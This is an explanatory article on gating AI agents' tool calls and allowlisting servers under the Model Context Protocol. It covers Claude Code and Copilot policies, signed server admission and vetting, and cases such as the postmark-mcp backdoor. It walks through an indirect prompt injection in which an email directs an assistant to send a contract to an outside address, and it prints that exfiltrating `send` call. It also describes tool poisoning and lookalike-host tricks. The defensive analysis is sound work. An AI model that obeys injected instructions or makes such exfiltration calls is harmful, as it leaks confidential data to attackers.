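# Tool-call gating and server allowlisting for AI agents: what enforcement at the protocol boundary can and cannot prevent

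## How an agent reaches a tool, and where a check can be placed

A language model only produces text. To send an email or open a file, it needs a program that reads part of that text as a request, carries out the request and returns the result to the model. A model that runs in such a loop is an agent, and a request to run one named operation with given arguments is a tool call. The tools often run on servers that neither the agent's developer nor its user wrote. Many connections to these servers use the Model Context Protocol (MCP), an open standard that the AI company Anthropic released in November 2024. The US National Security Agency's guidance paper *Model Context Protocol (MCP)* (2026) describes the protocol as the de facto standard for communication among AI services.

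Operators usually want to limit how agents use such tools, so they list the servers an agent's application may connect to and the tools the agent may call. They also place software between the application and the server to check every call before it goes out. Because these controls sit outside the model, text that reaches the model cannot override them. But this also limits the information they can use to the server, the tool name, the arguments, and any record the operator keeps of earlier calls.

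### The path of one tool call

The current revision of the MCP specification is dated 2026-07-28. According to the project's release post that day (Model Context Protocol, 2026), its main software kits were being downloaded nearly half a billion times a month. Model Context Protocol's *Architecture* (2026) divides the work among three kinds of program. The host is the application that runs the agent, such as a chat program or a coding tool. It creates clients inside itself, and each client talks to exactly one server. Servers offer tools. By design, a server should not see the whole conversation or the other servers, so only the host has access to all of it.

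For example, an employee might use an office assistant for correspondence. The assistant's host connects to a mail server with the tools `search`, `draft`, `send` and `delete`, to the company's internal file server with `search` and `read`, and to a web reader with `fetch`. The employee asks which of this morning's messages need an answer.

Before the model can call a tool, it has to learn what tools exist. Each client sends its server a `tools/list` request, and the server replies with a definition of every tool, which includes a name, a description in ordinary language, and a machine-readable schema of the arguments the tool takes. The host puts these definitions into the model's context. The model uses the description to decide when a tool is useful, so an attacker can hide instructions there (tool poisoning). A definition can also include annotations about the tool's behaviour, but *Tools*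 (Model Context Protocol, 2026), a chapter of the specification, requires clients to distrust them unless the server is trusted. The list of tools can change after the client first requests it.

The model then picks a tool, here the mail server's `search`, and writes the arguments. The host passes this choice to the client for that server, which sends a `tools/call` request with the tool's name and arguments. The server runs the search and returns the text of the morning's emails. The client passes this result to the host, which adds it to the context, and the model reads it before choosing its next step. The context now holds the employee's question, tool descriptions by three developers, and emails that could have come from anyone who knows the employee's address.

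MCP tools are designed to be "model-controlled", meaning that the model can find and call them without a person choosing each one. The MCP specification also states that there "SHOULD" always be a human who can deny a call. In technical standards, "SHOULD" marks a recommendation that an implementer may set aside for a good reason, while "MUST" marks a requirement.

### Local and remote servers

Messages can travel in two standard ways, which Model Context Protocol's *Overview* (2026) calls transports. With stdio, the client launches the server as a subprocess on the same machine, and the two exchange lines of text over the server's standard input and output. With Streamable HTTP, the client sends every message as an ordinary web request to one address, and the server may run anywhere. A local server typically serves one client, while a remote server typically serves many. Messages have the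 same meaning on both transports. In the example, the mail and file servers are remote and the web reader is local.

The transport affects where an operator can put a check. HTTP traffic crosses a network, so a company can route it through its own gateway. The July revision requires each HTTP request to repeat the method and tool name in two headers, `Mcp-Method` and `Mcp-Name`, so a gateway can allow or refuse the request without opening the message body. Stdio traffic doesn't cross a network, so a check on it has to sit in the host or in a wrapper program that the host launches in place of the server.

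Headers normally include the tool's name but not its arguments, so a gateway that reads only headers can distinguish `send` from `search` but not a colleague's address from a stranger's. A server's developer may mark individual parameters for copying into headers, but the specification advises against this for personal data, which includes a recipient's email address. A gateway must therefore parse the body to check where mail is going.

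If a request's header and body differ, a gateway that reads only the header could let it through as `search`, and the server could then run it as `delete`. A draft of the transport text from the Model Context Protocol project requires any server that processes the body to reject such a request. A mismatch is more of a concern with a faulty or hostile client than with a manipulated model, because the model does not write the headers.

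### Endpoint, user and agent

A "secure" connection can mean any of three things, which *Attested Tool-Server Admission* (Metere, 2026) distinguishes well. Metere works for Enclawed, a company whose product fills the gap he describes, but the distinction does not depend on the product.

An endpoint identity check confirms that the host reached the server named in the address. TLS, the encryption layer under https, does this with a certificate. The certificate proves that whoever runs the server controls the domain, but not that they have good intentions, and an attacker can obtain a valid certificate for their own domain.

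User authorization is a separate check on whether a person may use a server. MCP handles it with OAuth, the standard behind most "sign in with" buttons. The user signs in, an authorization server issues a token, and the client presents the token with its requests, acting on the user's behalf. A server may also limit its tool list to what the token permits. All of this is optional in MCP. The token establishes that the employee may send mail from this account, but not whether the assistant should send mail while it sorts the morning's messages.

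Neither a certificate nor a token establishes agent permission, which is whether a given agent may use a given server and a given tool on it. Under the architecture chapter, the host controls connection permissions and enforces security policy, but the protocol does not prescribe that policy. In the previous revision, Model Context Protocol (2025) stated that MCP "cannot enforce these security principles at the protocol level".

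Even the first two answers are unavailable with a local server, because a pipe between two processes has no certificate, and a stdio server is supposed to take its credentials from its environment instead of going through MCP's OAuth procedure. Endpoint identity then depends only on which program the host started and whether anyone replaced it on the disk.

The NSA made the gap a central complaint in a May 2026 paper, which describes MCP's security as "highly dependent on implementation discipline rather than protocol guarantees". According to the paper, MCP leaves it to the implementer to tie a session to an identity, and many implementations have no authentication at all. Those with authentication often lack roles, so they don't separate permission to read from permission to delete. MCP also has no way to exchange role-based permissions when a connection starts, which makes the boundaries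 between tasks hard to enforce or verify. Even where users must approve a server, its capabilities can often change later without a fresh approval.

The NSA criticized the November 2025 revision, and part of that criticism is now out of date. The July revision removed protocol-level sessions and tightened OAuth. Clients must now check which authorization server a reply came from, and may not reuse credentials issued by one authorization server with another. These changes strengthen user authorization but leave agent permission unchanged.

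These gaps are not obviously a defect. Metere calls them a matter of MCP's chosen scope, and a protocol could hardly contain the right policy, since a law firm and a games studio will want different things from the same mail server. But a standard way to state and verify a policy is a more modest request, and without one, two hosts connected to the same server can offer very different protection.

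### Prompt injection, tool misuse and the confused deputy

Even if the employee is entitled to read the company's files and send mail, the assistant needs permissions of its own because the model chooses the calls, and its choice depends on everything in its context, including text written by strangers. Prompt injection is text that makes a model follow an attacker's instructions. It is indirect when it arrives in content the agent reads, such as a web page, a document or an email, rather than from the person typing.

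Suppose one of this morning's emails comes from an outside address and looks like a routine note from a supplier. Further down, it contains instructions for the assistant to find the company's current contract with a large customer and send it to the sender "for review". The employee has not opened the email or asked for any of this. If the model follows the instructions, it calls `search` and then `read` on the file server, and finally `send` on the mail server, with the contract's text in the body and the outsider as recipient. Every certificate is genuine, the tokens are valid, and the employee is authorized to read that contract and to send email.

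Security engineers call a program in this position a confused deputy. It holds authority from one party, takes direction from another, and uses that authority for something the first party never intended. In 1988 Norm Hardy used the term for a compiler that had permission to write in a system directory, where it kept usage statistics. The compiler also let users name a file for its debugging output. One user named the system's billing file, which was in the same directory and which he could not have changed himself, and the compiler overwrote it. Hardy's remedy was to require whoever names a file to also supply the permission to write to it.

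The assistant is a confused deputy with a much wider range of tasks. It holds the employee's authority but in this case follows instructions from a supplier nobody has checked. Hardy's remedy does not carry over directly, because a language model receives instructions and data as one stream of text and cannot reliably treat the email as material to report on rather than as an order. Metere's threat model therefore classes the host as trusted and the model as untrusted, and assumes that an attacker controls part of what the model reads.

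Tool misuse is any harmful use of a tool the agent is permitted to call. Injection can cause it, and so can a dishonest employee or a simple error, as when someone asks the assistant to clear out old newsletters and it deletes correspondence with a client.

### The gate

A gate is software at the protocol boundary, the point where messages between host and server can be checked outside the model. For tool calls it amounts to a function,

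$$g(s, t, a, h) \in \{\text{allow}, \text{deny}, \text{ask}\}$$

where $s$ is the server, $t$ the tool, $a$ the arguments and $h$ the recorded state of the session so far. On "allow" the gate forwards the call. On "deny" it does not, and the agent receives an error. On "ask" it holds the call until someone decides. The simpler controls are special cases: a server allowlist looks only at $s$, and a tool allowlist at $s$ and $t$.

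The function needs $s$ as well as $t$ because tool names are supposed to be unique only within a server. In the example, two servers have a tool called `search`. The NSA reports that attackers have exploited such collisions to make applications load the attackers' code instead of the legitimate tool. The specification does not guarantee that the names servers give themselves are unique either, so the gate should identify a server by the address or launch command that the operator configured.

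The history $h$ is included because the same call can be harmless in one session and disastrous in another. In a March post on tool annotations, Model Context Protocol (2026) calls risk "a property of the session, not of any single server", since users routinely combine tools from several servers. To account for this, a gate must keep its own record of earlier calls, especially now that the protocol has no sessions, but its position limits what it can record. A gateway placed only in front of the mail server can record the outgoing message, but not that the agent read a contract a moment earlier. The host could supply that record, as could a single gateway that carries all the connections, provided the gateway can work out which calls belong together.

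A gate can filter the tool list as well as calls. If it removes `delete` from the reply to `tools/list`, the model normally won't try to call it. But the tool still exists on the server, and the model can produce its name from an email or from memory, so the gate must also block the call itself.

The specification distinguishes protocol errors, such as a call to an unknown tool, from execution errors, which clients should show to the model so it can correct itself and retry. If a gate reports its refusals as execution errors, the assistant can explain to the employee why it stopped. But a manipulated assistant can use the same error as a hint about what to try next, possibly by a route that does not pass through the gate.

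Microsoft's *MCP Security Gateway*, a specification for a gate of this kind, requires every component to deny on error. Otherwise, an attacker could open the gate by crashing it.

The July revision also lets a server interrupt a call to request input, such as confirmation before it deletes data. This resembles the gate's "ask", but the server decides when to use it. It can protect a user from a careless agent but not from a hostile server.

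When the assistant tries to send the contract, the gate receives a message like this one, shortened here:

```json
{
  "method": "tools/call",
  "params": {
    "name": "send",
    "arguments": {
      "to": "reviews@outsider.example",
      "subject": "Contract, as requested",
      "body": "[text of the contract]"
    }
  }
}
```

If the gate keeps a history, it also has the earlier calls: a mail search that returned a message from outside, a file search, and the reading of a contract. It does not have the model's reason for sending. The employee's job includes sending contracts to outside parties most weeks, often to addresses the company has never written to before, and the assistant's call to send one of those would have exactly the same form.

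## Server allowlists: deciding which servers an agent may connect to

A server allowlist takes effect when the host is about to connect to a server. If the server is not on the list, the host never loads its tools.

Without an allowlist, the user usually decides which servers an agent may connect to. Anyone who runs Claude Code, a coding agent, can by default connect it to any MCP server, according to Anthropic's *Control MCP server access for your organization*. Anthropic checks servers against listing criteria before adding them to its public directory, but it does not audit their security. Administrators can restrict the choice with two settings, `allowedMcpServers` and `deniedMcpServers`. In August 2026, GitHub's *MCP allowlists in enterprise managed settings* announced the general availability of settings with the same names for Copilot, GitHub's coding assistant. The two products use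 almost the same list format but combine the lists differently, so an administrator who assumes they work the same way can end up with a much weaker policy than intended.

### Matching by URL, command or name

An entry identifies a server in one of three ways. `serverUrl` matches the address of a remote server, `serverCommand` matches the program and arguments that start a local one, and `serverName` matches the label the server has in the user's configuration.

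A label does not reliably identify a server, because whoever writes the configuration chooses it. A user can call any server `github`, so Anthropic warns that a name entry "is not a security control", and GitHub describes name matching as a convenience. An attacker can exploit this without access to the user's machine, for example by publishing setup instructions that give a hostile server a familiar label. Microsoft's *Manage AI settings in enterprise environments*, which covers GitHub's policy in the code editor VS Code, notes that matching a name does not verify the server's command, endpoint or publisher.

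Both products therefore stop accepting a name match for local or remote servers once the allowlist contains a stricter entry for that type. If the list contains any URL entry, a remote server must match a URL entry, and if it contains any command entry, a local server must match a command entry. Suppose an administrator lists the name `github` and one approved launch command. Claude Code will refuse a local server called `github` that starts with a different command, but it will accept a remote server called `github` at any address, because the list has no URL entries.

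GitHub also has an older method, in which a company hosts a registry of servers and limits its developers to those. GitHub's *MCP server usage in your company* rates this method as weaker because it matches servers by name or ID, and users can bypass it by editing configuration files. In recent versions of VS Code, a managed allowlist overrides the registry for servers that the editor itself manages, so a server in the registry but not on the allowlist stays blocked.

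URLs are a better identifier, but one address can be written in several ways. GitHub's *Enterprise managed settings* describes how Copilot clients normalize both the entry and the server's URL before comparing them. They convert the scheme and host to lower case, turn international host names into their ASCII form, and remove default ports, fragments and trailing dots. They also decode percent-encoded characters in the host. Otherwise, a rule against `evil.example` would not match `%65vil.example`, which leads to the same machine.

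Wildcards need similar care. The entry `https://*.corp.example/*` should admit every server under the company's domain. If the first `*` could match a slash, the entry would also admit `https://attacker.example/x.corp.example/`, where the company's domain is only part of the path. GitHub's clients prevent this by stopping a wildcard in the host from matching any of the path. Even a correctly matched wildcard admits everyone who can publish under the domain, which is fine for a company's own domain but not for a hosting service that gives each customer a subdomain.

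An allowlist entry for a local server must match the server's command exactly, so `["npx", "-y", "server"]` does not match the same command with one more flag. (`npx` downloads a JavaScript package and runs it.) Matching covers only the command's text, so two servers with identical commands can run different code. Claude Code, for example, does not compare environment variables, some of which change what the JavaScript runtime loads at startup. A sample policy in GitHub's reference approves `npx @playwright/mcp@latest`, which still matches after the package's developers release new code.

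Policy entries in Claude Code may also contain variables such as `${HOME}`, which it expands before the comparison. A repository can carry its own settings file, which could otherwise redefine a variable in the company's policy, so Claude Code expands policy entries from a separate environment that project and user settings cannot change. The shell that launches Claude Code can still affect the expanded values, so Anthropic recommends literal URLs and commands for any entry that matters for enforcement.

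### Deny rules and a worked policy

A denylist blocks the servers on it and lets every other server through. By itself it offers little protection against an attacker, who can register a new domain in minutes. It is more useful for making exceptions to a broad allowlist. In both products, a denylist match overrides any allowlist match.

If nobody sets the `allowedMcpServers` allowlist, every server that passes the denylist loads, but if an administrator sets it to an empty list, only exempt servers load, such as those built into the product.

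Suppose the office assistant's host followed Claude Code's rules, and the company gave it this policy:

```json
{
  "allowedMcpServers": [
    { "serverUrl": "https://mcp.mailhost.example/*" },
    { "serverUrl": "https://*.corp.example/*" },
    { "serverCommand": ["node", "/opt/tools/web-reader.js"] }
  ],
  "deniedMcpServers": [
    { "serverUrl": "https://staging.corp.example/*" }
  ]
}
```

The host first tries to connect to the internal file server at `https://files.corp.example/mcp`. No deny entry matches this URL, but the second allow entry does, so the host connects.

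Next, the employee follows setup instructions from the web and adds a server labelled `files` at `https://files-corp.example/mcp`. Everybody in the company uses that label, but the address has a hyphen where the real one has a dot. No deny entry matches this server either. Because the allowlist contains URL entries, the label doesn't count towards a match. The address matches none of those entries, so the host refuses the connection.

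The third attempt is to connect to a test copy of the file server at `https://staging.corp.example:8443/mcp`. The host connects, even though the administrator wrote the deny rule to keep assistants away from this machine. In Claude Code, an entry with a full hostname covers only the default port (443 for https), while an entry with a wildcard in the hostname covers every port. The deny rule therefore doesn't cover port 8443, but the allow rule does. Changing the deny rule to `https://staging.corp.example:*/*` would block the connection.

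Mistakes like this are easy to make and hard to notice, since nothing fails. The opposite mistake is also hard to notice, because when a new policy blocks a server that a user had already configured, Claude Code drops it from the user's list without a warning. Anthropic advises administrators to tell people in advance.

### Combining policies from several sources

A client can receive settings from the user, from the company's device management system, and from the vendor's servers. Let $A_i$ be the set of servers that source $i$ allows and $D_i$ the set it denies. Under GitHub's rules, a client may run server $s$ only if

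$$s \in \bigcap_i A_i \quad \text{and} \quad s \notin \bigcup_i D_i,$$

where the intersection covers only the sources that define an allowlist. Adding a source can remove servers but never add one. An enterprise can loosen this deliberately by marking its lists as overridable, in which case individual teams may define their own.

Claude Code also takes the union of the denylists, but by default it takes the union of the allowlists too. The employee in the second attempt could therefore add `https://files-corp.example/*` to an allowlist in their own settings file, and the host would connect to the lookalike server. To prevent this, an administrator has to set `allowManagedMcpServersOnly`, which makes Claude Code ignore allowlists from users and projects.

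While the lock is on, Claude Code takes the allowlist from the highest-ranked administrative source that supplies one. A list delivered from Anthropic's servers replaces a list on the machine instead of combining with it. If an administrator turns on the lock but no administrative source supplies a list, Anthropic notes that in most cases every server that passes the denylist loads.

Some servers are exempt from the lists. Deny rules do not apply to GitHub's own servers. When Copilot runs in the cloud, its lists do not apply to servers defined in a repository's custom agent profiles, so administrators must block those servers' domains in a firewall to stop them. In Claude Code, built-in servers and most servers the organization provides are exempt from the allowlist but not the denylist. Servers that run inside the application that launched the session are exempt from both.

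An administrator can avoid much of this complexity with a file called `managed-mcp.json`, which gives every Claude Code user on a machine a fixed set of servers and stops them from adding others. The file can also fix the environment variables of local servers, which a command entry does not restrict. However, somebody in the company then has to handle every request for a new server. All of these policies work only if the client reads them.

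### When the policy is missing or broken

A gate fails closed if it blocks connections when it cannot determine the policy. GitHub says its server policies fail closed, so that a malformed or unverifiable configuration blocks servers.

A policy that can't be downloaded is harder to handle than a malformed one. Claude Code downloads centrally managed settings when it starts. Anthropic explains that if the download fails, Claude Code uses the copy from the last successful download, or runs without those settings if the machine has no copy. Any policy that device management has installed on the machine still applies. Even when the download works, the first session on a new machine can open before the settings arrive and briefly run without their restrictions.

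An administrator can set `forceRemoteSettingsRefresh` to make Claude Code exit if it cannot fetch a fresh policy. Copilot has a setting with the same name, which also rules out using an older cached copy. GitHub's statement about failing closed therefore covers a defective policy, but administrators have to turn on this setting to guard against an outdated one. Neither vendor makes it the general default, because a network fault or vendor outage would then stop every developer in the company from using the tool. A bank may accept that, while a small software firm would probably prefer to keep working under an outdated policy.

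When a policy is partly invalid, Claude Code generally drops the settings that fail validation and applies the rest, with a stricter fallback for certain settings. Dropping a denylist entry is riskier than dropping an allowlist entry, because it admits a server that an administrator meant to block, and probably nobody will complain. If an allowlist entry is dropped, somebody will complain that a permitted server is blocked.

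### Signed admission

A URL entry records that someone approved an address, but not who approved it or for what kind of data. Metere proposes a way to add both. His company, Enclawed, built the system so that its agent could use Google's mail, calendar and document servers, and ships it in two editions of its product.

In this scheme, a server publishes a short JSON document at a fixed path on its own site. The document lists the server's identity, publisher, version and clearance level, which is the most sensitive class of data the server may handle. It also identifies the key used to sign it and may list the hosts from which it is valid. The signature uses Ed25519, a public-key scheme in which only the holder of the private key can sign, but anyone with the matching public key can verify. It covers every field except itself, with the fields written in a fixed order so that the signer and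 verifier process the same bytes. If someone raises the clearance level after signing, the signature no longer verifies.

The host keeps its own set of trusted public keys, called the trust root. Each entry lists the levels the key's holder may vouch for and, optionally, an expiry date. The stricter edition locks the set right after startup, so a manipulated model cannot add a key during a session.

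Clearance levels form a ladder with numbered ranks. The default ladder begins with PUBLIC at 0, INTERNAL at 1, CONFIDENTIAL at 2 and RESTRICTED at 3, with two higher levels above. A hospital could use a different ladder that puts protected health information at rank 2. A server at level $s$ meets a required level $r$ exactly when

$$\operatorname{rank}(s) \geq \operatorname{rank}(r).$$

Before the host treats a connection as admitted, it runs eight checks and stops at the first failure:

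1. The document is well formed and declares that it belongs to an MCP server.
2. It contains a signature and the identifier of the signing key.
3. The key is in the trust root.
4. The key has not expired.
5. The trust root approves the key for the level that the document claims.
6. The signature verifies.
7. The server's level meets the level that the host requires.
8. If the document lists hosts, the host that the client connected to is one of them.

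Suppose the company requires CONFIDENTIAL for the file server, but the trust root approves the server operator's key only up to INTERNAL. If the operator signs a document that claims CONFIDENTIAL, the document fails the fifth check. If it claims only INTERNAL, it passes the fifth and sixth checks but fails the seventh. The operator cannot raise the server's level without a different key.

A server has to pass all eight checks, so their order doesn't affect the verdict, although Metere calls the order relevant to security. The order changes how much work the host does on a bad document and which reason for refusal goes into the log.

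The eighth check is optional but important, because the document is public and an attacker can copy it from an approved server and publish it on their own. If the document contains no list of hosts, the copy passes every check, and the host must rely on other protections to detect the substitution. Metere strengthened this part after his own tests exposed the weakness in an earlier version. He lists two related gaps as future work. The document has no expiry date, and hosts cannot check online whether a signing key has been compromised.

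Passing all eight checks admits the server but does not permit the use of any of its tools. The host keeps a separate entry for each server, with its address, the required level and a closed list of permitted tools. On every call, the host refuses any tool that is not on the list before anything reaches the network, and it repeats the clearance check. If the company listed `search`, `draft` and `send` for the mail server, a call to `delete` would fail even if the server advertised that tool. A server with no entry receives no calls, so the operator still has to maintain an ordinary server allowlist alongside the signed document. The document adds a statement from an identifiable signer about how sensitive the data may be, which an auditor in a regulated industry may well need.

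The stricter edition refuses a server that fails a check, while the open edition returns a warning and lets the host proceed, so its users get a record of the problem but may not be protected from it. Both editions log each decision and link the records with cryptographic hashes, so removing or altering a record later breaks the chain.

Google's servers motivated the work but do not use its central mechanism. Google publishes no signed document of this kind, so Enclawed's host skips the eight checks for these servers and relies on a separately signed connector that contains the address and the tool list. The Gmail server is therefore protected by a local allowlist that someone at Enclawed approved, much as it would be in Copilot or Claude Code, and by the tool list.

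### What Metere's tests measure

Metere reports that all 48 automated tests passed. In the 20 adversarial tests, the host refused all 31 altered tool names and all 12 invalid documents, each made by changing one thing in a valid document. It accepted the two valid documents and the two tool names that were on the list.

He then ran a much larger campaign, using the language model Llama 3.2 to generate the attacks. In 1,500 rounds, the model produced 27,025 distinct altered tool names meant to slip past the list, with tricks such as added spaces, chained commands and letters from other alphabets that look like Latin ones. In another 1,500 rounds, it produced 14,378 distinct forged documents that were well formed enough to test. The host refused all of the names and documents, and no refused tool call reached the network.

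The tool check compares two strings and refuses unless they are identical. Every name in the campaign differed from the names on the list, so a correct implementation would refuse all 27,025, or any larger number. These numbers therefore don't measure a success rate against attack. Metere makes a similar point, writing that the result is not a probability of denial. The campaign can reveal programming errors, such as trimming spaces or ignoring capitalization before comparing. That is worth testing, but the coverage is uneven. The category for changed capitals contains only 42 names, while about 45 percent of all names fall under "unclassified / other".

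The forged documents test even less of the system than their number suggests, because none of them could get past the sixth check. The model had no trusted private key, so it could not produce a valid signature, and the host stops at the first failed check. The evidence for the last two checks, on clearance levels and hosts, comes from the small set of handwritten tests, for which Metere had the necessary keys.

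The tests also don't include an attacker who uses a permitted tool on an admitted server. Metere excludes this case from the system's guarantees, along with inspection of the data that crosses an admitted connection, though Enclawed has other components for both. He also excludes hostile users who share one gateway and a model that declines to use a tool. Metere's company sells the system, so independent results would be more convincing, but the tests are part of the open edition and others can run them.

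He also ran the gate against Google's live Gmail server. The gate forwarded a permitted call that the model had chosen, and it refused a tool outside the list before contacting Google. This shows that the tool list works with a real service. The test did not cover the eight checks, which do not apply to that server.

Metere wants the MCP project to adopt the scheme as an optional extension. He argues that a signed document is useful only to hosts that agree on its format, and that only the project can establish one format for everyone. This seems right, and it explains why a server operator has little reason to publish such a document today. His paper is inconsistent about whether he has submitted the extension to the project. In one passage he describes it as not yet submitted, but in the acknowledgements he cites a numbered proposal in the project's repository.

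The charter of the Model Context Protocol's Security Interest Group lists server identity, signed assertions and trust roots among its discussion topics. The group assesses proposals and passes them to other groups. The charter does not mention Metere's scheme or any mechanism that the protocol's project has adopted. An operator who wants signed admission now would have to arrange it privately with each server.

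### The verdict on the supplier's email

A correctly written server allowlist stops the host from connecting to a server that nobody approved. If the supplier's email had told the assistant to install a "better" document search from the attacker's address, the list would have blocked it. In Claude Code, the command that adds an unlisted server fails with a policy error. The server's tool descriptions then never reach the model, so any instructions hidden in them have no effect, and the server cannot offer a `search` tool that the assistant might confuse with the real one. The list also protects against honest mistakes by employees, as with the lookalike file server.

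The theft needs only the company's own file and mail servers, so the actual email makes no such request. The host connected to both servers before the assistant opened the email, and both are on the allowlist because the employee needs them every day. Signed admission would not prevent the theft, even with a clearance level high enough for contracts, because both servers are entitled to handle them. The attacker runs no server in this case. The attacker's address appears only as the recipient in a call to `send`, and a server allowlist does not check recipients.

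## Vetted and unvetted servers: what a review establishes and when it expires

The company's mail and file servers are on the allowlist because somebody approved them, but their entries don't record what that person checked. The reviewer may have read the source code or only recognized the vendor's name.

A review can establish who operates a server, what its code does, what its tool descriptions tell the model, and what data its tools return. A reviewer can confirm one of these without learning anything about the others. Each check needs a date, because the server can change any time after approval.

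### The evidence behind each claim

Reviewers commonly rely on a registry listing, a signature, a code audit or a scanner. Each supports roughly the following:

| Evidence | Operator | Code | Tool descriptions | Returned data |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Registry listing | The name someone published it under | Nothing | Nothing, in the official registry | Nothing |
| Signature | Who holds the signing key | That it matches what the key holder signed | Only if the signature covers them | Nothing |
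| Code audit | Little | What one version does | Those in that version's source | Where it comes from, but not its content |
| Scanner | Nothing | Known bad patterns, with errors | Known suspicious phrases | Usually nothing |

The official MCP registry lets anyone publish a server under a name, which clients look up when they install it. For *Same Name, Different Server*, Kraishan (2026) downloaded the whole registry in August 2026 and found 21,643 servers with 72,606 version records. None of the records contains a tool definition, because the registry's format has no field for one. Kraishan also notes that the registry largely lacks the signing, proof of provenance and automated malware review that older package registries added over a decade.

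Anthropic's *How we contain Claude across products* describes ongoing review of the company's connector directory, and advises users to treat remote tools from anywhere else as untrusted and to try them on fake data first. This review is not a security audit, so a listing in the directory is only limited evidence that a tool is safe.

A signature shows that the holder of a particular key signed exactly these bytes. The Coalition for Secure AI's industry guidance, *Model Context Protocol (MCP) Security* (2026), recommends that developers sign their server code and publish a list of its components. This makes it harder to substitute other code, but a dishonest developer can still sign malicious code. The signed admission documents that Metere proposes add a sensitivity level but have the same limit.

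An audit is the best evidence about a server's code, but only for the version the auditor read. It cannot show what the server's tools will return, because that data often comes from strangers. Anthropic gives the example of a GitHub connector that passes every malware check and then loads a file with hidden instructions from somebody's repository.

### Tool poisoning

Suppose an attacker poisoned the description of the web reader's `fetch` tool with an instruction to add the subject lines of recent emails to every web address it requests. The code that carries out requests could be flawless, and a reviewer who read only that code would miss the attack, because it is an instruction to the model written in ordinary language. The Coalition for Secure AI also warns of attacks through the rest of a tool's schema, such as hidden parameters and malicious default values.

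The NSA describes a demonstration in which researchers targeted a trusted server for WhatsApp by connecting a second, malicious server to the same client. The malicious server's tool descriptions manipulated the client into exposing the user's WhatsApp messages without notice or approval. To make the attack harder to detect, the malicious server presented a harmless description at installation and switched to the malicious one after its second use.

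The WhatsApp server itself had no flaw for a review to find. The host had put descriptions from both servers into one context, where text from one could affect how the model used the other. The security of a vetted connection therefore depends partly on the other connections in the same host. If an administrator approves a mail server after careful review but lets employees add any weather or calendar server they like, the review protects much less than it appears to.

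### Name collision

The assistant's two `search` tools become a problem if the host indexes all tools by name in a single table. The server that connects later may then replace the other's entry, and the model's request to search the company's files would go to the wrong server. The operator of a hostile server can cause this deliberately by copying another tool's name.

According to the NSA, clients often cannot specify a unique tool or a strict rule for resolving names, so an outside server's responses can override a legitimate tool. Some applications also look up tool names automatically in public registries or local modules, and attackers have used this to load their own code. The NSA lists this among real-world problems but does not name an affected product or victim, so it is hard to judge how often it happens. A host can prevent basic name collisions by adding its own identifier for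 the server to every tool name.

A similar problem with package names is better documented. OSV's *MAL-2026-5481* (2026), a record in a public database of malicious and vulnerable packages, describes `mcp-server-postgres`, a package on npm, the main registry for JavaScript packages. It imitated the official MCP server for the Postgres database, whose package name begins with its publisher's prefix. When installed, the imitation ran a script that sent the computer's host name to an outside address.

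That script runs during installation, before the host requests a list of tools. An exact command allowlist can stop the host from installing and launching the package, but it can't stop a developer from installing it by hand. In either case, inspecting MCP messages would come too late.

### Definition drift and postmark-mcp

Definition drift is a change in a server's tools or their behaviour after someone has approved the server, even if the tool definitions stay the same.

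The best-documented case is `postmark-mcp`, an npm package that let an assistant send email through the delivery company Postmark. In September 2025 the security company Koi reported that versions 1.0.0 to 1.0.15 had worked as advertised, but version 1.0.16 added one line that sent a blind copy of every outgoing email to an address the developer controlled. OSV's *MAL-2025-47604* (2025) confirms the version and the method. Koi called it the first malicious MCP server found in real use.

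The gate could not have detected the change by inspecting the model's call to the mail tool, which contained the intended recipient, subject and body, just as before. The server added the extra recipient afterwards. Even a network filter that allowed connections only to Postmark would probably have let the copy through, because it was sent as part of a legitimate email.

The backdoor is well established, but the number of emails it stole is uncertain. Koi put downloads at 1,500 a week, guessed that 20 percent were in active use, and estimated that about 300 organizations were together sending 3,000 to 15,000 emails a day. The Hacker News (2025) reported 1,643 downloads in total. It also reported that the developer uploaded the package on 15 September and released the malicious version on 17 September, which doesn't fit Koi's account of a tool that teams had relied on for months. Koi sells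 a product that detects such changes and describes its impact figures as guesswork.

The package had a problem from its first version, although the case is usually told as a lesson that even a good server can turn bad. The developer had copied Postmark's official code from GitHub and published it on npm under the same name. Postmark said it had no involvement with the package and had not published an MCP server on npm before the incident. A reviewer who asked Postmark whether the package was theirs could have rejected it on the first day, even though any of the first fifteen versions would apparently have passed a code audit.

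The developer deleted the package from npm after Koi contacted him. That stopped new installations from npm but left the copies already on users' machines running.

### How often registry entries change

Among the 8,900 servers in the registry with more than one version, Kraishan found that 51 percent had changed their description, packages or network addresses between versions. In 41 percent, or roughly 3,600 servers, the change was "silent", meaning that the identifiers stayed the same while the meaning or destination changed. Most of this is less alarming than it sounds, because 3,242 of these servers had changed their description, which is the registry's summary of the server, not the tool descriptions that the model reads.

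A more serious change affected 370 servers, or 4.2 percent, which kept their names in the registry but moved their remote addresses to different hosts. Kraishan assumes most of these were routine migrations and has no evidence that any was malicious. But neither the registry nor a client can distinguish a migration from a takeover. An allowlist that matches full URLs would block the new address until someone approved it, while one that matches names would accept it.

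Kraishan also reports that among servers that changed, the median time to the first change was zero days. He appears to measure from when the developer publishes the server, and developers often fix mistakes in the first hours. A user who installs the server six months later may find it quite stable, so the figure does not support his conclusion that an install-time review typically describes a server that had already changed the same day.

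### Code that a reviewer can pin

An operator can read the source of a local server, choose one version and refuse all others (pinning). Someone who had pinned `postmark-mcp` to version 1.0.15 would not have received the backdoor. A remote server runs on its provider's machines, so the provider can change it at any time, and the user has no copy to compare. Anthropic draws this contrast and concludes that a decision to trust a remote tool at installation may not hold later.

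Pinning a server by version number alone is weak because it fixes only the server's own package. The server may depend on dozens of other packages, and if its developer specified a range of versions for them, a fresh installation can bring in new code. The Coalition for Secure AI therefore recommends pinning dependencies by cryptographic hash. It also recommends reproducible builds, which let a reviewer confirm that the package was built from the published source.

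Even pinned code can behave differently from day to day if it takes instructions or data from the network. For example, the output of the company's local web reader depends on the page it fetches. A local program that sends its work to an online service is in practice partly a remote server, and the reviewer should treat it as one.

A local server can also do more damage. It normally runs with the permissions of the user who launched it, so a malicious one may be able to read files unrelated to its tools. Anthropic at first ran local servers inside the virtual machine that isolates Claude Cowork, its desktop agent for office work. It later moved them out, partly because the virtual machine made them harder to audit and partly because some needed access to programs on the user's computer. The servers are now less isolated, and Anthropic treats them like any other software a user might install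 and lets administrators decide which to allow.

Kraishan's scanner flagged 2.1 percent of remote servers and 1.3 percent of local ones for code that claims overly broad permissions or forwards a user's credentials to another service. These figures are not corrected for false alarms. The difference is small, but a forwarded credential matters more on a remote server because it ends up on a machine the user doesn't control.

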